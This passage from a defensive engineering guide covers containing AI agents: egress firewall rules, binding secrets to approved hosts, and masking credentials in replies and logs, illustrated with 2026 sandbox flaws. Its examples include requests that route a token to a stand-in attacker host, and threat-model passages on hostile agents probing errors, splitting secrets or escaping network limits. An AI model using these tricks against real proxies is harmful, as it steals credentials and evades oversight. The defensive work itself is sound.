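In October 2026 the security startup AIR reported a flaw in Vercel's sandboxes that no list of approved destinations could have stopped. *Sandbox vulnerability gives rogue AI agents a path to escape* (Smalley, 2026) explains that a specially made certificate could cause an approved server to contact an unapproved one and pass information to it. The sandbox never connected to the unapproved server, so the firewall detected nothing unusual. AIR's co-founder Niv Hoffman said that Vercel needed time because it was unclear how to fix the flaw. Vercel did not immediately respond to Smalley's request for comment. AIR found no sign that anyone had exploited the flaw but couldn't rule it out.

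In this case and in both of Docker's, the policy named one set of destinations and data could reach another. Tuttle lists two more examples, an empty allowlist that allowed everything and a hostname that a policy engine and a proxy interpreted differently. Commey's confusion of names and objects occurs on networks as well as in file systems, and the remedy is similar. The component that checks the destination should also make the connection:

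1. It converts the hostname to a standard form, since `GitHub.com`, `github.com` and `github.com.` all mean the same site.
2. It compares the result with the allowlist.
3. It looks up the address itself and checks it against the blocked ranges.
4. It connects to that address without a second lookup.
5. It compares the SNI field, and the `Host` line if it can read it, with the name it approved.

The component should fail closed, meaning that it refuses the connection if any step gives no clear answer. Vercel's firewall blocks all traffic when a policy lists no destinations. But if a policy adds credentials for certain domains and also allows all others, connections without a readable hostname pass through unchanged. Docker found a similar problem in its command-line tool, which applied a network rule with an empty sandbox name to every sandbox. The tool has rejected such commands since version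 0.51.0.

These five steps wouldn't have prevented the flaw AIR found, because the firewall correctly identified the connection's destination. TLS termination should help because the sandbox's encrypted connection then ends at the intermediary and the approved server never receives the sandbox's certificate. The intermediary must also refuse certificates from the sandbox, or it could make the extra request itself.

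### Acme's rules

The microVM for Acme's shop agent has no network card. It has one virtual link to the model gateway and one to the GitHub proxy. The second team's microVM has neither link.

The intermediary needs a check outside itself, because an attacker who takes it over can ignore any allowlist inside it. The server's firewall can't do this alone, since it filters by address. Acme therefore adds an exit filter, a small proxy that holds no secrets and runs under its own account. The filter follows the five steps, then relays encrypted traffic it can't read. It listens on a different port for each component, and each port has its own allowlist.

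| Component | What it can reach | How Acme enforces this |
|---|---|---|
| Shop agent's microVM | Model gateway and GitHub proxy | No network card, and one link to each |
| Shop agent's microVM during setup | `registry.npmjs.org` | A temporary link to the exit filter |
| Model gateway | `api.anthropic.com` | Exit filter, port 3101 |
| GitHub proxy | `api.github.com` and `github.com` | Exit filter, port 3102 |
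| Program that issues GitHub tokens | `api.github.com` | Exit filter, port 3103 |
| Exit filter | Acme's DNS resolver, and port 443 at public IPv4 addresses | Server's firewall |

The secrets are in files on the same server, so the secret store needs no network rule. If Acme moved them to another machine, it would add a line for that machine's address. On Linux, the firewall's part of the policy looks like this:

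```
table inet agents {
  chain forward {
    type filter hook forward priority filter; policy drop;
  }
  chain output {
    type filter hook output priority filter; policy drop;

    ct state established ct direction reply accept

    meta skuid "gateway"  ip daddr 127.0.0.1 tcp dport 3101 accept
    meta skuid "ghproxy"  ip daddr 127.0.0.1 tcp dport 3102 accept
    meta skuid "ghtokens" ip daddr 127.0.0.1 tcp dport 3103 accept

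    meta skuid "exit" ip daddr 10.0.0.53 udp dport 53 accept
    meta skuid "exit" ip daddr 10.0.0.53 tcp dport 53 accept
    meta skuid "exit" ip daddr != { 0.0.0.0/8, 10.0.0.0/8,
        100.64.0.0/10, 127.0.0.0/8, 169.254.0.0/16,
        172.16.0.0/12, 192.168.0.0/16 } tcp dport 443 accept
  }
}
```

`inet` makes the table cover both IPv4 and IPv6, and `policy drop` discards any packet that no line accepts. If somebody gave a microVM a network card by mistake, the `forward` chain would stop its traffic. In the `output` chain, `skuid` identifies the account that runs a program. No line accepts traffic from the account that runs the microVM, so an attacker who escaped into that account would still have no network access. No line lets a program start an IPv6 connection or send a `ping`. The server needs extra lines to update its own software and synchronize its clock.

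The line about replies accepts only reply packets, and outgoing packets must still match the current rules. Many firewalls instead accept every packet on an established connection, so removing a permission there doesn't cut off a connection that is already open.

Acme should load the table when the server starts, before any microVM starts, and refuse to start one if the table is missing. Otherwise a restart could undo the policy, as it did with Docker's ICMP block. On the intermediary's side, malware in the gateway could still try domain fronting through the model provider's servers, and the exit filter wouldn't detect it because it can't read the `Host` line.

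### Opening the registry only during setup

The agent's code needs packages from npm, but the agent doesn't need constant access to the registry. A registry accepts uploads as well as downloads, so an injected instruction could make the agent publish the shop's code as a package under an attacker's account. Cloudflare gives an example in which the operator opens GitHub and npm, runs `npm install`, and then blocks all web traffic. Acme can do much the same, leaving only the links to the gateway and the GitHub proxy:

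1. A launcher outside the sandbox starts the microVM with all three links but without the agent.
2. The launcher downloads the reviewed main branch through the GitHub proxy. It installs the exact package versions in the project's lock file, with the packages' install scripts turned off.
3. It removes the registry link, closes any connection still open on it, and ends every process that setup started.
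4. It tries to reach the registry from inside the microVM, and deletes the microVM if the attempt succeeds.
5. It runs any install scripts the project needs, then starts the agent.

Turning off install scripts keeps them from running a package's code while the registry is still open. If the agent later needs a new package, it can propose a change to the lock file. After a person approves the change, the launcher builds a new microVM.

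Operators who use a hosted sandbox should set a network policy when they create it, because some sandboxes, including Vercel's, start with full access by default. Vercel applies later policy changes to the running sandbox before saving them for future sessions. If the save fails, the running sandbox has the strict policy, but the next session may start with the old one. The launcher should therefore check for errors after each change and repeat step 4 after every restart.

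### The same rules in Kubernetes

Kubernetes' built-in firewall rule, the NetworkPolicy, applies to a whole pod (a group of containers that share one network address), so a sidecar can't have its own egress rule. If Acme puts the agent and the intermediary in the same pod, a policy that blocks the internet also stops the intermediary from reaching GitHub, while one that allows GitHub lets the agent connect there directly.

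Waldrep found this problem in a working cluster of five agents, described in *Per-Pod NetworkPolicy in Practice*. Proxy variables directed each agent's traffic to its own sidecar for scanning. But the pod's policy allowed internet access because the sidecar needed it, so an agent could clear the variables and bypass the scan.

The remedy is to put the intermediary in a pod of its own. This policy applies to every pod in the agent's namespace and allows connections only to the gateway and the GitHub proxy:

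```
apiVersion: networking.k8s.io/v1
kind: NetworkPolicy
metadata:
  name: agent-to-intermediary
  namespace: shop-agent
spec:
  podSelector: {}
  policyTypes: [Ingress, Egress]
  egress:
  - to:
    - namespaceSelector:
        matchLabels:
          kubernetes.io/metadata.name: intermediary
      podSelector:
        matchLabels:
          serves: shop
    ports:
    - {protocol: TCP, port: 8443}
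    - {protocol: TCP, port: 8080}
```

The second `podSelector` has no dash in front of it, so a pod must match both the namespace and the label. With a dash, the policy would allow every pod in the intermediary's namespace, plus any pod with that label in the agent's own. The policy also blocks DNS. Operators often add a rule that lets pods use the cluster's resolver, but that resolver may forward queries to the internet. Instead, Acme can write the intermediary's fixed address into the agent's pod.

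Waldrep moved all five agents in about a day. The first took four hours and the fourth less than one, and each separate scanner used about 50 MiB of memory. Waldrep ran every bypass test on the first agent but only some of them on the other four, and later regretted it. The scanners' new policy let them reach any address on ports 80 and 443, so the move confined the agents but not the scanners that handled their traffic. NetworkPolicies can't filter by hostname, so Acme would put its exit filter in a third pod and let the intermediary's pod connect only to that.

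Setup also has to change, because the pod's policy applies to Kubernetes init containers, which do preparatory work before the main container starts. Some of Waldrep's init containers downloaded a program from the internet and failed as soon as the new policy took effect. Waldrep had them copy the program from a container image instead. Acme can likewise build its packages into the agent's image, or install them in a separate pod that it deletes before the agent starts.

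According to Kubernetes' *Network Policies*, a NetworkPolicy has no effect unless the cluster's network plug-in supports it, and Kubernetes accepts the policy without an error either way. Policies can only add permissions, so a broad policy that someone else writes for the same pod overrides Acme's narrow one. A pod can always reach the machine it runs on, so Acme shouldn't leave an administration interface listening there. The plug-in also determines how ICMP is handled and whether a policy change affects connections that are already open. Acme should therefore replace the agent's pod after tightening a policy, and test from inside the new one.

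## Binding each secret to approved destinations and callers

Acme's network rules limit where the intermediary can connect, but they don't decide which secret goes with which request. The GitHub proxy can reach `api.github.com`, and without a further check it would attach the shop's token to requests from any program that could connect to the proxy. Acme therefore needs destination binding, the rule that the intermediary may attach a given secret only to requests for named upstream services. It also needs a rule for callers, so that only the shop agent's sandbox can use the shop's secrets.

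### The check before every request

A binding is an entry in the intermediary's rules that ties together a caller, a secret, a mechanism and a list of hosts. Acme has two, one for the gateway and one for the proxy:

```
caller       secret         mechanism   hosts
shop-agent   model key      API key     api.anthropic.com
shop-agent   GitHub token   app token   api.github.com, github.com
```

The mechanism matters because many services accept more than one kind of secret. Besides API keys, a service may support OAuth, in which a person signs in on the service's own site and a program receives an access token that lets it act for that person. API keys and OAuth tokens can grant different permissions and be meant for different hosts. Docker's built-in settings for Anthropic, for example, cover four domains, including the chat site `claude.ai`, where an API key has no use. When a third-party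 configuration asks for a credential, Docker records the approved domains for API keys and OAuth separately, and approval for one doesn't apply to the other.

Before it attaches a secret, the intermediary goes through five steps:

1. It identifies the caller from the connection that the request arrived on, and refuses unknown callers.
2. It converts the destination's hostname to a standard form, and refuses any request that doesn't use HTTPS.
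3. It looks for a binding that lists this caller, this mechanism and exactly this host, and refuses if there is none.
4. It attaches the secret in that binding and no other.
5. It connects to the host it has just checked, verifies the host's certificate, and sends the request.

Here are three requests to the GitHub proxy:

| Sandbox | Request | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Shop agent | `GET https://api.github.com/repos/acme/shop/issues` | The proxy attaches the GitHub token |
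| Shop agent | `GET https://api.github.com.attacker.example/repos/acme/shop/issues` | The proxy refuses at step 3, because no binding lists this host |
| Second team's agent | `GET https://api.github.com/repos/acme/shop/issues` | The proxy refuses at step 3, because no binding lists this caller |

The hostname in the second request starts with GitHub's address but belongs to whoever owns `attacker.example`. A proxy that compared only the start of the name would send the token there, and one that compared only the end would accept `notgithub.com`. The third request shouldn't be possible, since the second team's microVM has no link to the proxy, but the binding protects the token if somebody adds a link by mistake.

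The component that holds the secrets must refuse to use any secret whose binding is missing or empty. Before version 0.51.0, Docker's proxy attached user-defined secrets even if they had no destination hosts. When a configuration needs a credential and nobody is present to approve it, as on a build server, Docker now starts the sandbox without the credential and prints a warning, although the job may then fail.

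Operators should also check what happens when they remove a secret. In Docker's sandboxes, a secret can belong to one sandbox or to all of them. If an operator removes a sandbox's own secret, the sandbox falls back to the shared one, which may have more authority. At Acme, removing a caller's secret should leave the caller with no other secret to fall back on.

HTTPS is required because anyone on the network path can read an unencrypted request. Docker's proxy adds no credentials to plain HTTP requests, but it forwards them with any credential the agent supplied. An agent could therefore send a stranger's key to an approved service that still accepts plain HTTP. Acme's proxy refuses all unencrypted requests.

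### Where the address comes from

The caller must not be able to choose the upstream address. The API server of Crawl4AI, an open-source program that collects web pages for language models, let callers choose it. CodeAnt AI's *Credential Exposure (CWE-200) in Crawl4AI Docker API* describes the flaw, CVE-2026-56259. Callers could set `base_url`, the address for calls to the model, and in another field write `env:` followed by the name of an environment variable. The server would then send that variable's value to the address they had chosen.

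Anyone who could reach the server could therefore choose both the secret and its destination, without logging in. One of the available secrets was the key the server used to sign its login tokens, which would let an attacker forge logins. The flaw scores 8.2 out of 10 on CVSS 3.1, the standard severity scale.

CodeAnt AI recommends authenticating callers, checking `base_url` against a strict allowlist, and taking keys only from the server's own configuration. Acme relies on the gateway's fixed upstream address, because the caller it worries about is its own agent, which would pass authentication.

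A caller can sometimes alter even a fixed address. Suppose that the gateway builds the full address by adding the caller's path to `https://api.anthropic.com`, and accepts a path that doesn't start with a slash. The agent sends the path `@attacker.example/v1/messages`, and the result is:

```
https://api.anthropic.com@attacker.example/v1/messages
```

Web software treats the part before the `@` as a username, so the key goes to `attacker.example`. Acme's exit filter would block this connection, but the gateway shouldn't depend on that. It should store the host and the path as separate values and set the `Host` header from its own configuration.

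Using wildcards also gives up control of the address, because they approve every matching name, including names that don't exist yet. In Docker's rules, `*` stands for one part of a hostname and `**` for any number of parts. A binding to `**.amazonaws.com` would cover every API that customers publish through Amazon's API Gateway, including any that an attacker publishes from their own account. Wildcards are risky even for domains that a single company controls, because an old subdomain may still point to a hosting account that the company has given up and someone else can claim.

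Docker warns that its default network rules include broad wildcards such as `*.googleapis.com`, which covers many services besides AI. Overly broad network rules give the agent more places to send data, and the same breadth in a binding can expose the secret itself. Even a list of exact domains may include more than the agent needs. Docker's built-in GitHub settings attach the token to requests to six domains, including `gist.github.com`, but Acme's agent needs only two.

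### Redirects and token endpoints

An upstream service can also redirect a request to a different address, and many programs follow redirects automatically. Most web libraries drop the `Authorization` header when the new address has a different host, but they often keep less common headers such as `x-api-key`. An attacker who controlled the service's replies could use such redirects to collect keys.

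The intermediary should therefore never follow a redirect itself. It can pass the redirect back to the agent's program, and if the program follows it, the new request goes through all five steps. A redirect from HTTPS to plain HTTP on the same host then fails at step 2.

Some redirects are part of normal work. When a program asks GitHub's API for an archive of a private repository, GitHub redirects it to `codeload.github.com` with a temporary link that works without a token. Acme has no binding for that host, so the download fails. This is acceptable because the agent gets its code with `git`. If the agent needed archives, Acme should permit the host without binding a secret to it.

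Other secrets go to a second address by design. A program that uses OAuth usually receives a refresh token along with its access token. When the access token expires, the program sends the refresh token to the service's token endpoint to get a new access token. The endpoint may be on a different host from the API, so it needs its own approval.

Container registries, which store container images, make this harder because the registry's reply specifies where the program exchanges its password for a token. An attacker who took over the registry could name their own server. Docker's proxy accepts the address automatically only if it is on the registry's own host or is paired with that registry in a built-in list. The operator has to approve any other address, and the proxy then requires HTTPS and the exact host and path, so approval for `/jwt/auth` doesn't cover `/jwt/auth/`.

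The intermediary must also recognise a token endpoint reliably, because the endpoint's replies contain new secrets. stack.watch's *Docker Sandboxes*, a list of recorded flaws in the product, includes a failure to do so, CVE-2026-105570. Docker's proxy ignored capitalisation in the hostname when routing a request, but not when checking whether to hide the tokens in the reply. Code in the sandbox could therefore change the hostname's capitalisation and still reach the genuine provider. If the user then completed the sign-in, the sandbox could receive the real access and refresh tokens. Converting the hostname at step 2 prevents this only if every later decision uses the converted name.

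Acme has one exchange of this kind, in the small program that gets hourly tokens from GitHub. That program may send its proof of identity to only one path at `api.github.com`.

### Identifying the caller

Step 1 works only if a hostile caller can't impersonate another caller. A header such as `X-Sandbox: shop-agent` doesn't prove the caller's identity, because any program can set it.

Many local intermediaries listen on a port at `127.0.0.1`, the address a machine uses to connect to itself, and serve any program that connects. Other machines can't connect, but any process on the same machine can, whichever account it runs under, because a port has no file permissions. On a developer's laptop, a web page in the browser may also be able to send requests to the port. If the intermediary attaches Acme's token to all these requests, every sender has the token's authority.

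Docker's clone mode had a similar unauthenticated port, which users fetched the agent's work through. According to Docker, connections of this kind expose the repository and its history to other accounts on the machine. Version 0.54.0 replaced the port with a socket that only the user's own account can open, although an optional setting restores the port for older Git programs.

Acme gives each sandbox its own socket. The launcher creates the socket, connects it to one microVM, and registers it with the intermediary under that sandbox's identity. Every request on the socket therefore comes from that sandbox, and the agent holds no proof of identity that anyone could steal. On Linux, the intermediary can also use the kernel to check which account opened the connection, and reject any account except the one that runs the microVM.

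The folder that holds the sockets needs protection too, because a program that can replace a socket can impersonate the intermediary. stack.watch lists a flaw, CVE-2026-126329, in which Docker's background program reused existing folders without checking who owned them. If an administrator ran it as root while its settings pointed to another user's folder, that user could replace sockets and configuration files and possibly run commands as root. Docker fixed this in version 0.53.0. Since version 0.51.0, Docker's command-line program on Unix systems has checked that a socket belongs to the same account before sending anything through it.

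Local sockets don't work across machines, so if Acme moved the intermediary to a separate host, the launcher could create a random token for each session and give it to both the sandbox and the intermediary. The agent's programs would send the token over an encrypted connection in the `Proxy-Authorization` header, and the intermediary would remove it before forwarding the request. For the gateway, a placeholder unique to each sandbox can serve the same purpose.

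A session token is itself a bearer credential, so anyone who steals it and can reach the intermediary can use the GitHub token's authority until the session ends. Acme would also need a firewall rule that accepts connections only from the machines that run its sandboxes, and it should cancel each session token when its sandbox stops.

In a large cluster, the orchestrator can identify each sandbox instead. Kubernetes can give a pod a signed, short-lived token that names the pod's account and the one service that should accept it. The intermediary checks the token's signature, expiry time and intended service, then looks for a binding for that account. Unlike the automatic token that Acme turned off, this one doesn't work with Kubernetes' own interface. A client certificate is harder to steal in transit because the sandbox proves it has a private key without sending it. Malicious code in the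 sandbox could still copy the key.

None of these methods can distinguish the agent from a malicious package in the same sandbox, so the binding has to permit only requests that would be acceptable from either.

### Docker's unchecked approvals

On November 30, 2026, Docker fixed a flaw in its sandboxes that let an attacker collect API keys without breaking out of a sandbox or reading its memory. Peyton Kennedy, a researcher at the security company Endor Labs, had found that Docker recorded the destinations a user approved but never checked them. Endor Labs' *CVE-2026-136998* announced the flaw the same day.

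The flaw concerned kits, which are packaged configurations for agents. A kit can specify which service's key the agent needs and where Docker's proxy should send it. Users don't have to approve built-in kits, but since version 0.43.0, released on September 15, Docker has asked them to approve credentials for third-party kits. The Hacker News' *Docker Sandboxes Flaw Lets Malicious AI Agent Kit Updates Steal Developers' API* (2026) explains what went wrong afterwards.

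Suppose a developer at Acme uses a third-party kit. When the kit first runs, Docker requests permission to use the Anthropic key at `api.anthropic.com`. The developer agrees, and Docker records the service and domain in a file. A month later, the kit's author, or someone who has taken over the author's account, publishes an update that changes one line, replacing Anthropic's address with the attacker's.

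When the developer next created a sandbox from the kit, no prompt appeared. The proxy checked only that an approval existed for the service called `anthropic`. It then took the destination from the new version of the kit and sent the real key there. The sandbox's network allowlist did not block the request, because the kit could add the attacker's server to it without a prompt.

Kennedy demonstrated this with a dummy key and a test server on the same machine. The key arrived unencrypted, so a strict HTTPS rule would have stopped that test, but an attacker could have used an HTTPS server. The approval remained in force after Kennedy deleted the sandbox. Two other protections worked. A third-party kit couldn't impersonate a built-in agent, and the approval prompt still defaulted to refusal.

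Thirteen built-in services, including Anthropic, OpenAI, GitHub and Google, shared the faulty code, but Kennedy tested only Anthropic. Every sandbox on the machine can use the stored keys by default, so a stolen key would usually be the one all the developer's agents used. The research covered sandboxes on users' own computers, and nobody has established whether Docker's cloud version ever had the flaw.

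Docker's log would have been little help to an investigator. It recorded an allowed connection to the attacker's server but didn't show that the proxy had attached a key. (A later section covers what such logs should record.)

Endor Labs rated the flaw 8.2 out of 10 on CVSS version 3.1, while Docker rated it 5.6 on version 4.0. Kennedy first calculated 9.3, then lowered the score to 8.2 because the malicious kit is a file that the developer fetches, so the attack counts as local. Kennedy's score on version 4.0 is 6.9, which is in the medium range, as is Docker's.

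The remaining difference comes from an assumption about which losses to count. Version 4.0 scores harm to the flawed product separately from harm to other systems. Docker counted a serious loss of confidentiality in its own product and no harm elsewhere, according to its entry in the public register, which Intruder's *CVE-2026-136998* (2026) reproduces. Kennedy also counted harm to the account that the stolen key opens. Acme should use Kennedy's assumption, because it protects the token to prevent a thief from doing damage in its GitHub account.

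Nobody had reported an attack by early December. SC Media's *Docker sandboxes vulnerability exposes developer API keys* (2026) advises users to upgrade, review the approvals they have given, and replace their keys if they detect suspicious activity. Waiting for suspicious activity isn't cautious enough when the log can't show whether a key left the machine. Anyone who ran an updated third-party kit on an affected version should replace every key the kit could have redirected.

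### Approving changes to third-party configurations

Since version 0.55.0, Docker has enforced the destinations in each approval, and it prompts the user again when a kit requests additional domains. Approvals are still stored by service, in a file with no field for a kit's name or version, so an approval for one kit appears to cover any other kit that requests the same service at the same domains. The second kit could then use a GitHub token at GitHub, though it couldn't send the token to an attacker's server. An approval should also record which configuration it is for.

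A configuration's name isn't enough to identify it, because the contents of a tag, branch or folder can change. *Docker Sandboxes Flaw Let Malicious AI Agent Kits Steal Developers' API Keys* (Faisal, 2026) relays Endor Labs' advice to treat repeated runs from such a reference as a reason for review. If Acme used third-party kits, it could record each kit's digest, a checksum of its exact contents, and keep using that version until someone had reviewed the next one.

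People who are asked to approve every update soon stop reading the prompts. In September 2026, Docker published a new kit specification with a compromise. Agentic AI Foundation's *Docker Sandbox Kit Spec* explains that updates can be approved automatically if they don't widen the agent's permissions, while changes in access are revealed at update time. This saves effort, but it depends on comparing the old and new permissions correctly, and it can't detect an update that uses the same permissions for something harmful.

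When a person has to decide, the prompt should show which secret the configuration requests, which hosts will receive it, and what has changed since the last approval. When a program requests a new network destination, NVIDIA's OpenShell shows the host, port and program, and the approval lasts only for the session. Limiting credential approvals to the session would have ended the one that outlived Kennedy's sandbox. Reviewers should also check settings other than the host list, since a Docker kit can include `passthrough: true`, which sends real OAuth tokens into the sandbox.

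Restricting where configurations come from gives some protection. By default, Docker installs kits only from Docker Hub, its public registry, but anyone can open an account there and publish. Signatures confirm who published an update but not that the update is safe, as the malicious LiteLLM release showed.

Acme keeps its bindings in a file that only its administrators can change, and the intermediary reads the destinations from that file on every request. A third-party configuration can specify a new host, but the intermediary will not send the secret there until an administrator adds that host to the binding.

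## Stopping the secret from coming back in responses and logs

Acme's bindings send the GitHub token only to GitHub, but they don't control what comes back. If a reply contains the token, or anything that works in its place, the agent can read it. According to Infisical's *Agent Proxy*, credentials that the proxy attaches "cannot be exfiltrated, logged, or memorized from inside the agent", but this holds only if no reply or log brings them into the sandbox.

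### Replies that repeat the request

Some services copy the request's headers into an error message to help programmers find their mistake. If GitHub did this, a malformed request from Acme's agent might get this answer:

```
{"error": "bad request",
 "received": {"Authorization": "Bearer REAL-TOKEN"}}
```

A hostile agent can search for such errors by sending overlong headers or invalid values. It can also try the HTTP method TRACE, which instructs a server to return the request as received. Acme's proxy should refuse TRACE, but Acme can't predict every error message.

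The best protection is to bind secrets only to services that don't repeat them. Varlock's *Credential proxy*, the manual for another product that replaces placeholders, advises operators to assume that an agent can recover a secret from any approved service that repeats it. Debugging endpoints are the most likely to do so. Kenney and colleagues found no credential in the replies from three echo services, which return whatever they receive, but none of the three was an approved destination, so the intermediary had never attached a credential. The test supports destination binding but doesn't cover what happens when an approved service repeats the headers it receives.

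### Searching replies for the secret

An intermediary can also search each reply and mask the secret before the agent receives it. Docker does this for user-defined secrets:

1. The proxy puts the real value into a request header and sends the request.
2. When the reply arrives, the proxy checks whether it can search it. If the reply is only part of a file, or uses an encoding that the proxy doesn't support, the sandbox gets an error (502) instead.
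3. The proxy searches the headers and the body for the secret in its original form and in three common encodings.
4. It masks every match and passes the reply to the sandbox.

The encodings matter because services rarely copy text unchanged. A made-up secret, `blue/heron"42`, could come back in any of these forms:

```
original          blue/heron"42
JSON-escaped      blue/heron\"42
percent-encoded   blue%2Fheron%2242
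base64            Ymx1ZS9oZXJvbiI0Mg==
```

Base64 converts three bytes at a time, so the same secret can produce different characters depending on how much text precedes it. Git joins a username to the token before encoding both, so a filter that searches only for the token encoded on its own may miss it. Acme's filter should search for the encoded secret in all three possible alignments.

Masking can't be complete, because a service can transform a value in endless ways. Suppose the secret is `blue-heron-4217` and a service returns it in two fields:

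```
{"part1": "blue-her", "part2": "on-4217"}
```

Neither field matches, and the agent only has to join them. A service could also return the secret backwards or with spaces between the letters. Docker's filter also ignores WebSocket messages, and it works only on requests where the proxy has inserted a user-defined secret. By that description, Docker would not mask a GitHub token that the user stored under its built-in GitHub service.

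An ordinary text search also misses secrets in Git downloads, because Git compresses files in its own format. Git adds a checksum too, so changing the contents would make it reject the download.

### Partial and compressed replies

HTTP lets a program request a range of bytes, for example to resume an interrupted download. The server answers with status 206, Partial Content. If a file contains the secret, the agent can request everything up to the middle of the secret and then everything after it. Each response would contain only half of the secret, so the filter would not match either one.

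Masking also interferes with the download, because replacing the secret with a mask of a different length changes the byte positions the program uses to assemble the file. Varlock lets partial replies through unsearched for this reason. Docker's refusal is safer, although it breaks programs that depend on ranges. Acme's proxy can often avoid the problem by deleting the `Range` header from the request, since servers may ignore that header and send the whole file. The proxy should still refuse any partial reply.

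An agent can also use compression to get around a filter. Varlock searches only uncompressed text of up to 2 MB, so a hostile agent can turn off the search by adding an `Accept-Encoding` header that asks for a compressed reply. Acme's proxy should overwrite that header to ask for uncompressed replies, and refuse any reply it can't decode.

The proxy should search even large replies. It can search them in chunks, as long as it holds back the end of each chunk and searches it again with the start of the next. Otherwise a secret split across two chunks would get through.

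### Why short secrets can't be masked

Suppose a service identifies its callers by a four-digit code, and Acme's code is 2026. A filter that masked every "2026" in the replies would also mask the year in most of the dates.

It would also reveal the code, because the agent could post a comment listing all 10,000 possible codes, read it back, and see which one was missing. Docker requires user-defined secrets to have at least eight characters and no longer inserts existing ones that are shorter. Eight random letters and digits allow about 218 trillion combinations, far too many to list. But length doesn't help if the secret is a word or a date, because the agent can still list the likely guesses. Acme should replace any such secret with a random one.

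Because of the same trick, a filter shouldn't try to catch split secrets by masking short fragments. If it masked the first three characters on their own, the agent could guess the secret three characters at a time.

### Text that the service stores

An agent may also be able to make the service store the secret and then read it later. If an intermediary replaced placeholders in request bodies, the agent could post a GitHub comment containing the placeholder, and GitHub would save the comment with the real token in it. Masking might hide the token in the immediate reply, but everyone with access to the repository could still read it on GitHub. The agent could also fetch the comment later by a route that the filter doesn't cover. With Docker's filter, a request without a placeholder would be enough if the stored object was public, because the proxy would insert no secret and so wouldn't search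 the response for one.

Replacing placeholders only in named headers prevents this leak. A service uses the `Authorization` header to check who is calling and doesn't save it as content, while the comment reaches GitHub with the harmless word PLACEHOLDER still in it. Docker's proxy now works this way, but it used to replace placeholders anywhere in a request, and an early version of its manual, *Credentials*, recommended user-defined secrets for credentials that belong in a request body.

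The operator has to name the headers because services store some of them. Amazon S3, for example, saves any header that begins with `x-amz-meta-` along with the uploaded file and returns it with each download. If an intermediary replaced placeholders in every header, the agent could store a secret this way and then read it back.

Some services accept a secret only in the request body. Blaxel's *Proxy secrets injection* describes a proxy that adds fields to JSON requests, using names and values the operator sets. The proxy never searches the agent's own text for placeholders, so the agent can't choose where in the body the secret goes. The agent may still choose which request receives the extra field, and for some requests the service stores everything in the body. An operator who needs this method should restrict it to the one path that requires the secret, such as a login.

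### Signed addresses and cookies

A reply can also contain a credential that the intermediary has never seen, which a search for known values will miss. When a program asks GitHub's API about a file in a private repository, the reply includes a `download_url`. For a short time, anyone with that address can download the file without Acme's token. Other services use signed addresses in the same way for large uploads and downloads.

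Acme's proxy can delete `download_url` from GitHub's replies, because the agent gets its files through `git`. If the agent did need such links, the proxy could keep the real address, give the agent a local one, and fetch the file itself. Either method works only for fields that somebody has identified, and a new version of the API may add more. A link that the proxy misses usually does limited damage, because it soon expires and opens only one file, which the agent could already read. An outsider benefits only if the agent can pass the link on before it expires.

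Session cookies can be more serious. Some services include a `Set-Cookie` header in their response to an authenticated request, and the cookie then works like a password for the rest of the session. Acme's proxy should remove that header from responses. If a service needs the cookie, the proxy can store it and attach it to later requests under the same binding as the original secret.

### OAuth logins

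In an OAuth login, the service's reply is supposed to contain new secrets. The intermediary should therefore complete the exchange itself:

1. The user signs in on the service's website, and the service issues a one-time code.
2. The intermediary sends the code to the approved token endpoint over HTTPS.
3. It stores the access token and the refresh token outside the sandbox.
4. It gives the agent's program a reply in the expected format, with placeholders instead of tokens.
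5. When the program sends a placeholder to an approved host, the intermediary attaches the real access token. It renews that token when necessary.

Docker's proxy works this way for several coding agents and rejects any exchange over plain HTTP, at the first sign-in and at each renewal. Anthropic's hosted agents have a vault that stores OAuth credentials for MCP servers, along with their expiry times and the details needed to renew them.

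In step 4, the intermediary has to identify the fields that hold secrets. Docker's support for third-party kits requires the service to return its refresh token in a field called `refresh_token`. If the intermediary only edits the fields it recognises, it will let through a token with any other name. It's safer for the intermediary to write a new reply that contains only the placeholders, the token type and the expiry time. This also leaves out the ID token, a signed statement of who the user is, which some services accept as a credential.

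The one-time code needs protection too. If the login starts in the sandbox, malicious code there may be able to copy the one-time code and anything else the exchange requires, then send them to an accomplice who redeems the code first. Starting the login outside the sandbox avoids this. In Docker's sandboxes, OpenAI's Codex prompts the user to log in on the host computer, while Claude Code, Cursor and Droid prompt inside the sandbox.

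The proxy lets Acme's agent reach `github.com`, which also hosts GitHub's OAuth endpoints. The agent could start a login there, persuade an employee to approve it, and receive a real token for that employee's account. The agent never needs to log in, because a separate program gets its GitHub tokens, so the proxy should refuse every path under `github.com/login/`.

Docker's `passthrough: true` setting turns this protection off and delivers the service's real reply to the sandbox. Operators may want it for a program that has to read its own token. But the agent then holds a working token, so they lose most of the intermediary's benefit. If the reply includes a refresh token, a thief may be able to keep renewing access until somebody revokes it. Operators who turn on passthrough should use an account with very few permissions and revoke the tokens when the task ends.

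Tokens can also enter a sandbox without passing through the intermediary. Docker introduced SSH access to its sandboxes on July 24, 2026, and five days later released a version that stopped SSH sessions from copying variables such as `OPENAI_API_KEY` and `GH_TOKEN` from the user's computer into the sandbox. The next version fixed a similar leak of OAuth tokens from Anthropic's desktop app. Acme should search a running sandbox for real credentials after adding any new way to connect to it.

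### Debug messages and logs

The intermediary's own error messages also go to the agent, so they should contain only fixed text and a reference number, with the details in a log outside the sandbox. When Docker's tool fails to fetch a secret from a password manager, it hides the password manager's error output by default because that output may contain sensitive information. An option displays the output for troubleshooting, which is reasonable on an administrator's screen but not in a reply to the agent.

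An agent can still read a log kept outside the sandbox if someone later brings it in. A developer may paste a failed request into the agent's session, or Acme may give another agent a tool for searching the company's logs. Support files can even leave the company. Diagnostic bundles, for example, can go to Docker, which began removing account names and home-folder paths from them in November 2026. The log must therefore be safe to read even for someone who shouldn't have the secrets.

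The simplest way to keep the secret out of the logs is to write the log entry before adding the secret to the request. The entry then contains the placeholder, which identifies the sandbox that sent the request. Replies and errors need separate treatment because they arrive after the secret is added.

Removing only the headers known to be sensitive is unreliable, because many services use custom headers for their keys. In *Sanitizing options for custom headers*, a thread on the forum of the app-building platform Retool, users complained that its debugging output hid the `Authorization` header but displayed custom headers. A Retool employee replied that the problem should be fixed, but in October 2023 another user could still see the headers. A reply in another thread, *Security issue/question*, confirmed that one of Retool's endpoints exposed custom headers and said it probably exposed URL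 parameters as well.

Acme should instead list the fields that its log may contain and discard the rest. A second filter can search each entry for known secrets before writing it, with the same blind spots as response masking. Kenney and colleagues recommend removing authorisation headers, cookies, secrets in queries and signed addresses, while keeping the connector's identifier, the policy decision and the identifiers that link related events. Applied to Acme, with some additions, the list looks like this:

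| Data in the request or reply | What the log keeps |
|---|---|
| The secret | Its name and version number, but no part of its value |
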